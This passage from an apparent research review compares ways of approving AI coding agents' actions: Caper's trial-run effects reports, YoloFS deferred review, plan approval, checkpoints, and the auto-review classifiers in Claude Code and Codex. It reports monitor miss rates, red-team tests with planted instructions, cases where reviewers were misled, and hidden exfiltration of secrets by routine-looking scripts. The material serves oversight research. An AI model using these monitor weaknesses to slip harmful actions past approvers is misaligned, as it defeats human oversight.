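The models caught 30 per cent of attacks from the description, mainly because some descriptions repeated the suspicious detail, such as a web address that imitated a familiar one. When the description left out the extra recipient, the models never caught the attack. No reader could have done better, since some harmful and harmless requests had identical descriptions. The 16 per cent refusal rate is partly due to the test's use of placeholder text instead of real messages, which the models gave as the reason for most refusals. Without those refusals, the rate would be about 2 per cent.

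These results concern language models and provide little evidence about people. The researchers also used simulated human approvers, which are simple programs with assumed habits. One compared the card with the task. Attacks with a false description succeeded against it 3 per cent of the time when it saw the card and 54 per cent when it saw only the agent's text. Another believed the agent's explanation whenever it was on the screen. Attacks succeeded against it 54 per cent of the time even with the trusted card, but 5 per cent once the researchers removed the explanation. Removing the explanation hardly changed the 15 language models' answers.

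The researchers acknowledge that these figures follow largely from the habits they built in, but the figures show that a study of people would have to test whether developers, with only a few seconds to spend, read the agent's friendly sentence and skip the card's accurate fields. If they do, labeling the sentence as untrusted may not protect them. Showing it only after they have looked at the command might work better, much as Buçinca and colleagues had people decide before seeing the AI's advice, though it would also annoy developers more.

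Generating the text from the request makes the display faithful. For an email or a payment, it also does much to make the display understandable, but it helps less with a shell command. For the log command, fixed rules could show the full path of the current folder and warn about the deletion and the push, but they couldn't list the files in the commit without inspecting the repository. For `make clean`, the card would accurately show `make clean`, which would tell the person nothing new.

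## Asking about effects, plans or finished changes instead of commands

Someone who sees only `make clean` has to open the Makefile to learn what it will delete. Software could instead run the command in a protected environment and show her what changed. In other designs, she approves a whole plan before the agent starts, or the finished changes at the end. Sandboxes and automated review are meant to keep approval requests to a minimum.

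### Running the command first

Wu and colleagues built Caper, a system that decides on each command after a trial run. The agent works in a container with the network switched off, and Caper goes through five steps for every shell command the agent proposes.

1. It takes a snapshot of the container.
2. It runs the command under system-call tracing, which records what each program asks the operating system to do, such as open a file or connect to a server. Caper holds back the output, so the agent doesn't see it yet.
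3. It boils the trace down to a short effects report. This lists the files that changed, attempted connections, what the command printed, and any reads of password files or keys. For small text files it includes a diff.
4. A separate AI model, the approver, reads the report along with the user's request, the conversation and the command, and then allows or blocks the command.
5. If the approver allows it, Caper keeps the changed container and passes the output to the agent, so the command has run only once. If the approver blocks it, Caper restores the snapshot and gives the agent the reason, and the agent can try another way.

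In one task, the agent proposed `python3 scripts/check-deps.py`, which looks like a routine check of the packages a project depends on. The trial run showed that the script read the project's `.env` file and tried to connect to outside servers. The approver blocked it because a dependency check doesn't need to do either. The full trace of that command was 165 KB, and the report was 3.4 KB. Half of all reports were under 1 KB.

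Wu and colleagues compared Caper with six existing systems, using the same AI model as the agent each time. They ran 682 tasks from SABER and the 102 hidden-damage tasks described earlier, each paired with a harmless version. One of the six checks commands against fixed rules, and three are guardrail models, which classify text as safe or unsafe.

| System | Harm on SABER | Harm in hidden-damage tasks | Harmful commands blocked | Harmless twins blocked |
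|---|---|---|---|---|
| No approval | 19.7% | 71.6% | – | – |
| CARE (fixed rules) | 15.0% | 69.6% | 2.0% | 2.0% |
| TS-Guard (guardrail model) | 18.8% | 94.1% | 8.8% | 8.8% |
| gpt-oss-safeguard (guardrail model) | 18.6% | 62.7% | 14.7% | 15.7% |
| Qwen3Guard (guardrail model) | 16.0% | 67.6% | 0% | 0% |
| Claude Code's auto mode, with a substitute classifier | 14.8% | 62.7% | 3.9% | 3.9% |
| YoloFS (undo after the fact) | 21.2% | 35.3% | – | – |
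| Caper | 6.7% | 7.8% | 84.3% | 1.0% |

The systems that judged only text blocked harmful commands and their harmless twins at almost the same rate, so being stricter wouldn't have helped them. TS-Guard blocked 39 per cent of all the commands in these tasks, but only 9 per cent of the ones that did the damage. Without a trial run, Caper's own approver also blocked most of the twins, but with the effects report it blocked one in 102.

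The effects report did not make up for a weaker approver, though. When Wu and colleagues used a weaker model as approver, the report cut the share of twins it blocked from 54 to 5 per cent, but harm rose from 25.5 to 33.3 per cent because the model blocked less of everything. Removing the diffs from the report also raised harm under the stronger approver, from 7.8 to 13.7 per cent. The increase came entirely from overwritten files, which a list of changes shows only as files whose size has changed, whereas it shows deletions directly.

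The benchmarks favour Caper in some ways. Wu and colleagues built the hidden-damage tasks themselves, and the damage is always a lost or overwritten file, which a before-and-after comparison shows very well. They also corrected SABER's scoring rules after finding false alarms in them, although Caper had the lowest harm under the original rules too (9.0 per cent against at least 16.0). Each system ran each task only once, and neither benchmark includes an attacker who adapts to Caper. On SABER, the agent safely completed 48.6 per cent of tasks with Caper, compared with 57.4 per cent when nothing restricted it.

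More importantly for approval by people, no person took part in the test of Caper. A report like Caper's should make a command much easier to understand. It also makes the display faithful in the strictest sense, because Caper keeps the very changes that the report describes. The reader would still have to compare those changes with what she wanted and keep paying attention. A typical report has about 900 characters and takes perhaps half a minute to read. The agent needed about ten decisions per task, so reading every report would take around five minutes a task. Volunteers who used the Consent Ledger caught more harmful requests when they could see recorded facts, which gives some reason to expect that effects reports would help people too.

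Caper can only undo what happens inside the container. Suppose it ran the earlier command that deletes old logs, commits everything and pushes the result. Caper's report could list the deleted logs and show that the commit included `.env.backup`, and it would record the attempt to contact the server. But the push couldn't succeed during the trial, because the network is off. Someone would have to let it run outside the trial, and then nobody could undo it. The same goes for emails, payments and changes to a remote database. For these, a trial run can make the approval request more informative, but the person still has to decide before the action happens.

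### Reviewing finished changes

Zhong and colleagues, who collected the 290 reports of agents misusing files, designed YoloFS, a file system that sits between the agent and the user's files and puts off most questions until the end of the session. When the agent edits, deletes or renames something, YoloFS records the change in a separate area and leaves the original alone, but the agent's later commands behave as if the change had happened. At the end of the session, the user runs a review command that lists every file the agent added, modified, deleted or renamed. She can then commit the changes to her real files, discard them or leave them for later. The agent can't commit them itself.

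YoloFS also takes a snapshot after each command and shows the agent what the command changed, so the agent can go back if something looks wrong.

Reading a secret can't be undone, so YoloFS prompts the user before sensitive reads. The prompt names a file instead of a command. In the example of the malicious Rust package, a conventional prompt shows only `cargo build`. YoloFS lets the build start, pauses it when a script inside tries to open the user's SSH key, and asks whether to allow that read. The user doesn't need to know how `cargo` works to see that a build has no reason to read her SSH key. If she doesn't answer in time, YoloFS denies the read.

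Zhong and colleagues tested this on 11 small projects in which a routine command does hidden damage. Without YoloFS, Claude Code let the damage happen in ten and asked the user about the other. With YoloFS, it noticed and reversed the damage in eight, but saw the changes and accepted them in the other three. In one of those three, a deployment script copied the source code to a staging folder and then deleted the original, which Claude took for normal deployment behaviour. In another, an installation script replaced the project's settings, and Claude judged the new contents "safe and expected".

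Those three sets of changes stayed in the holding area, where a user could still have rejected them, but nobody tested whether users would. They are the hard cases because they look like part of the job. The projects also had only 10 to 41 lines of code. In a real session, the replaced settings file might be one entry among hundreds.

Wu and colleagues' comparison gives an idea of how much damage would be left for the person to catch. The agent undid something in 66 of their 102 hidden-damage tasks, but 35.3 per cent of all 102 still ended with damage in the state the user would receive. On SABER, their version of YoloFS did slightly worse than no approval at all, because undoing changes can't recover a password that has left the machine. That version gave the agent the change summaries and undo commands but blocked nothing, so this result isn't evidence against YoloFS's prompts for sensitive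 reads.

Compared with approving commands one at a time, a final review needs the user's attention once, shows the actual changes to the files, and commits exactly those changes. It also lets the user compare the whole result with what she asked for. YoloFS also reduced interruptions during the work. On 112 simple file tasks, it needed 0.4 prompts per task, against 0.9 for Claude Code, 1.3 for GitHub Copilot and 2.2 for Google's Gemini tool. Codex, with its sandbox, also needed 0.4.

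A final review doesn't prevent effects outside the file system. If the log command ran under YoloFS, the deletions would wait for review, but the push would already have sent the database password to the server. Asking for approval at the end also doesn't guarantee that anyone reads the list of changes. GitHub reviewers also see finished changes, and they became more likely to approve them as they gained experience.

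### Approving a plan

An agent can instead present a plan before it starts work. Users reject 39 per cent of Claude Code's plans, so they evidently read them. A plan for the log task might say that the agent will delete logs older than a week, commit the result and push it. A developer with unfinished work could reply that she doesn't want a push, even if she knows no Git.

The causes that Zhong and colleagues identified in their 290 reports suggest which mistakes a plan could expose. In 76 reports, the agent pursued the wrong goal, for example by deleting files that the user wanted archived. If the plan lists the deletion, the user has a fair chance to object. In 50, the agent understood the task but went too far, and a plan would reveal that only if it stated the limits of what the agent would do. In 27, the agent used a tool incorrectly, as when it tried to delete a file named `~`. No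 plan would show that mistake, because it arises only when the agent writes the command.

Plan approval therefore helps most with attention and comparison. It helps less with effects, since "commit the result" leaves out the same facts as a one-line summary does. It also falls short on faithful display, because the user approves the plan rather than the commands that run. Zhou, Roy and colleagues (2025), in *When Should Users Check?*, watched eight people supervise commercial agents on tasks such as booking travel and editing images. The most frequent error was a mismatch between what the agent said it was doing and what it did. In one case it logged a click on 4 July, while the screenshot showed 9 July. An agent that misreports a click can also depart from a plan it wrote earlier.

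### Choosing when to ask

An agent could also stop for checks between the plan and the final review. Zhou and colleagues worked out where to place these stops to save the user time. In their first study, people who found a wrong result went back to the start, looked for the first mistake, told the agent how to fix it and waited while it redid the rest. The later people check, the more steps they have to search and the more the agent has to repeat, but checking too often also wastes time.

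Suppose each step succeeds with probability *p*, and the person checks after *n* steps. The chance that the first mistake comes at step *m* is the chance that the earlier steps all succeeded multiplied by the chance that this one failed. She then inspects *m* steps to find it, and the agent repeats that step and every later one. If a check takes *c* seconds, inspecting one step takes *d* and redoing one step takes *r*, the expected cost of the check and any repair is:

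```
c + sum over m = 1 to n of  p^(m−1) · (1−p) · [ m·d + (n−m+1)·r ]
```

The researchers' method adds the expected time for the steps that remain and picks the checkpoints with the lowest total. Their shopping task had eight steps, each with an 87.5 per cent chance of success, and redoing a step took 20 seconds. With a single check at the end, the agent could expect to repeat about 3.4 steps, which takes 68 seconds. A second check after step four would bring that down to about 2.2 steps, or 44 seconds. That check is worth making if it takes less than 24 seconds, even before counting the time saved in searching for the mistake. (These figures leave out any new mistakes during the repairs.)

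Zhou and colleagues then had 48 people from a university supervise a simulated agent that shopped, edited images and played a cooking game. With checkpoints placed by the model, tasks took 229 seconds on average, 13.5 per cent less than with one check at the end. Thirty-nine people preferred the checkpoints. Nearly all the time saved came from tasks with early mistakes, which took about 29 per cent less time with checkpoints. Tasks with mistakes in the middle took about 2 per cent less time, and those with late mistakes took 4.5 per cent more. Each check also took 38 per cent less time, because people only had to consider the latest steps.

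Checks like these should help with attention and understanding, since the person looks at a few recent steps when she expects to be asked. They don't protect her from a step that does lasting harm, because she sees it only after it has run. The agents in this study also failed in six of every seven trials, so people had good reason to check the agents' work.

With a more reliable agent, the same calculation would favour having no extra checks. If each step succeeded 999 times in 1,000, the eight-step task would lose less than a second on average to repeated work, so no extra check would save time overall. Skipping the checks is reasonable when a mistake wastes 20 seconds, but not when it deletes a customer database. Zhou and colleagues therefore suggest including money and risk when measuring the harm from a mistake, and requiring a check before high-stakes actions however accurate the agent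 is.

### Sandboxes

Sandboxes reduce the number of approval requests. Most of the Codex actions in OpenAI's snapshot stayed inside the sandbox and needed no approval. Having fewer requests should help people pay attention to those that remain, but it doesn't make them any clearer. In Zhong and colleagues' hidden-damage tasks, Codex's sandbox stopped the commands, and Codex then asked to run them outside it. The request showed the command but none of its hidden effects, so the researchers didn't count these cases as harm prevented.

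A sandbox also needs upkeep. One that is too tight stops test suites and builds from running, and users who keep getting offers to run commands outside it may switch it off. The documentation for OpenAI's *Auto-review* advises adjusting the boundary first. Users can add the folders the agent needs and allow exact commands such as `cargo test` instead of everything that starts with `python`. Rules written in advance can still leave people less protected, as they did in Yan's experiment.

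### Automated review in Claude Code

In auto mode, software answers the questions that remain. According to Anthropic, the agent can read and search files without any check, and the user's narrower allow rules still apply. The agent can also edit files inside the project, since the user can review those changes later in version control. A classifier checks shell commands and other actions with more potential for harm.

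The classifier first makes a quick yes-or-no decision that errs towards blocking. Only the actions it flags go to a second stage, where the model reasons before deciding. More than twenty default rules describe what to block, including destroying data, sending code to outsiders, weakening security and releasing software to live systems. The classifier then checks whether the user clearly asked for the action. A request to "clean up my branches", for example, doesn't authorise deleting a whole batch of them.

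The agent receives the reason for each block. After three blocks in a row, or 20 in a session, Claude Code goes back to asking the person.

Anthropic published these error rates in March 2026:

| | Ordinary actions blocked (of 10,000) | Real overreaching actions missed (of 52) | Invented data leaks missed (of 1,000) |
|---|---|---|---|
| First stage alone | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Both stages | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

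The second stage makes auto mode bearable to use but lets more harmful requests through. If 10 requests in 1,000 were harmful, the first stage alone would let through fewer than one of them and block about 84 harmless ones. Both stages together would let through about two harmful requests and block four harmless ones. The 17 per cent miss rate is uncertain because it is based on only 52 actions, about nine of which were missed. With a sample that small, the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from roughly 9 to 30 per cent.

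Anthropic says in its August post that the classifier now checks whether a `git push` is going to a public, private or trusted repository, and that it looks at the state of the repository before a command that could discard unsaved work. These facts are among those missing from the text of the log command, and they would help a person answering a prompt just as much.

Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, helped Anthropic find weaknesses in its classifier by inserting invented attacks into records of real coding sessions. After Anthropic strengthened the classifier, the share of attacks it missed fell from 12 to 7 per cent. On the part of the test that used attacks Anthropic had never had access to, the new version caught about half of the attacks the old version had missed, but missed about 2 per cent of those the old version had caught. Apollo designed the attacks to find failures,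 so the 7 per cent figure is weak evidence of the miss rate in ordinary work.

Anthropic made auto mode the default for new Claude Code sessions on its Pro, Max and Team plans from 14 August 2026, and said in October that it would do the same in most of its other Claude apps. Its argument that auto mode is safer than a typical user relies heavily on the experiment with 1,053 paid testers.

Automated review replaces most approval by a person rather than making it more meaningful. The classifier doesn't get tired, and it can work out many effects faster than a developer can. Of the four conditions, comparison remains the weak point, because the classifier has to infer what the user wanted from what she typed, and it sometimes infers too much. The user gets involved again only after the classifier has blocked the agent several times, and by then she may have lost track of what it was doing.

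### OpenAI's version and outside tests

In Codex, Auto-review is a second Codex agent that judges only requests to cross the sandbox boundary. Unlike Anthropic's classifier, it receives the first agent's visible messages and tool outputs, and it can look things up without changing anything. Trębacz and colleagues report that Codex stops to ask a person about 200 times less often with Auto-review than in manual mode.

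In their tests, which used mostly invented cases, the reviewer refused 99.3 per cent of the actions that followed planted instructions to run code or send out data. When they included deletions and tampering with data, the rate fell to 90.2 per cent, though they say many of the added cases weren't serious. They also found cases where the reviewer could be misled into approving commands, and they warn against treating it as a guarantee of security.

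OpenAI gives users an unusually narrow way to overrule the reviewer. The user picks an action from a list of recent refusals, which permits one retry of that exact action. The retry still goes through the reviewer, which can refuse again if the policy doesn't let users make exceptions of that kind. Unlike "don't ask again", this approval covers only one concrete action, which software has already marked as doubtful. How well people choose from that list is unknown.

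Outsiders have done little testing of either product. Anthropic paid Trajectory Labs to run 72 scenarios with planted instructions, ten times each. None of the attacks succeeded against three recent Claude models in auto mode, while 5.83 per cent succeeded against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol with Auto-review. Without auto mode, only 0.09 per cent succeeded against the same Claude models. So almost all of the resistance came from the models, and the test shows little about what auto mode adds. A competitor commissioned the comparison with Codex, and OpenAI released a new version of Auto-review before Anthropic published the result.

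Wu and colleagues' test is independent of both companies, but it didn't use Anthropic's classifier model. They ran the official Claude Code program with an OpenAI model, GPT-5.6 Luna, as the classifier and another company's model as the agent, so the 62.7 per cent harm rate in the hidden-damage tasks doesn't measure the product customers use. When they replaced auto mode's checks with Caper and kept the same two models, harm in those tasks fell to 6.9 per cent. That supports their view that the missing evidence mattered more than the choice of model. They left out Codex because most of the harm in their tasks happens inside the project folder, which Auto-review doesn't check.

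Anthropic advises developers to personally review high-stakes changes to live systems, which now requires switching to Manual mode before the work begins.
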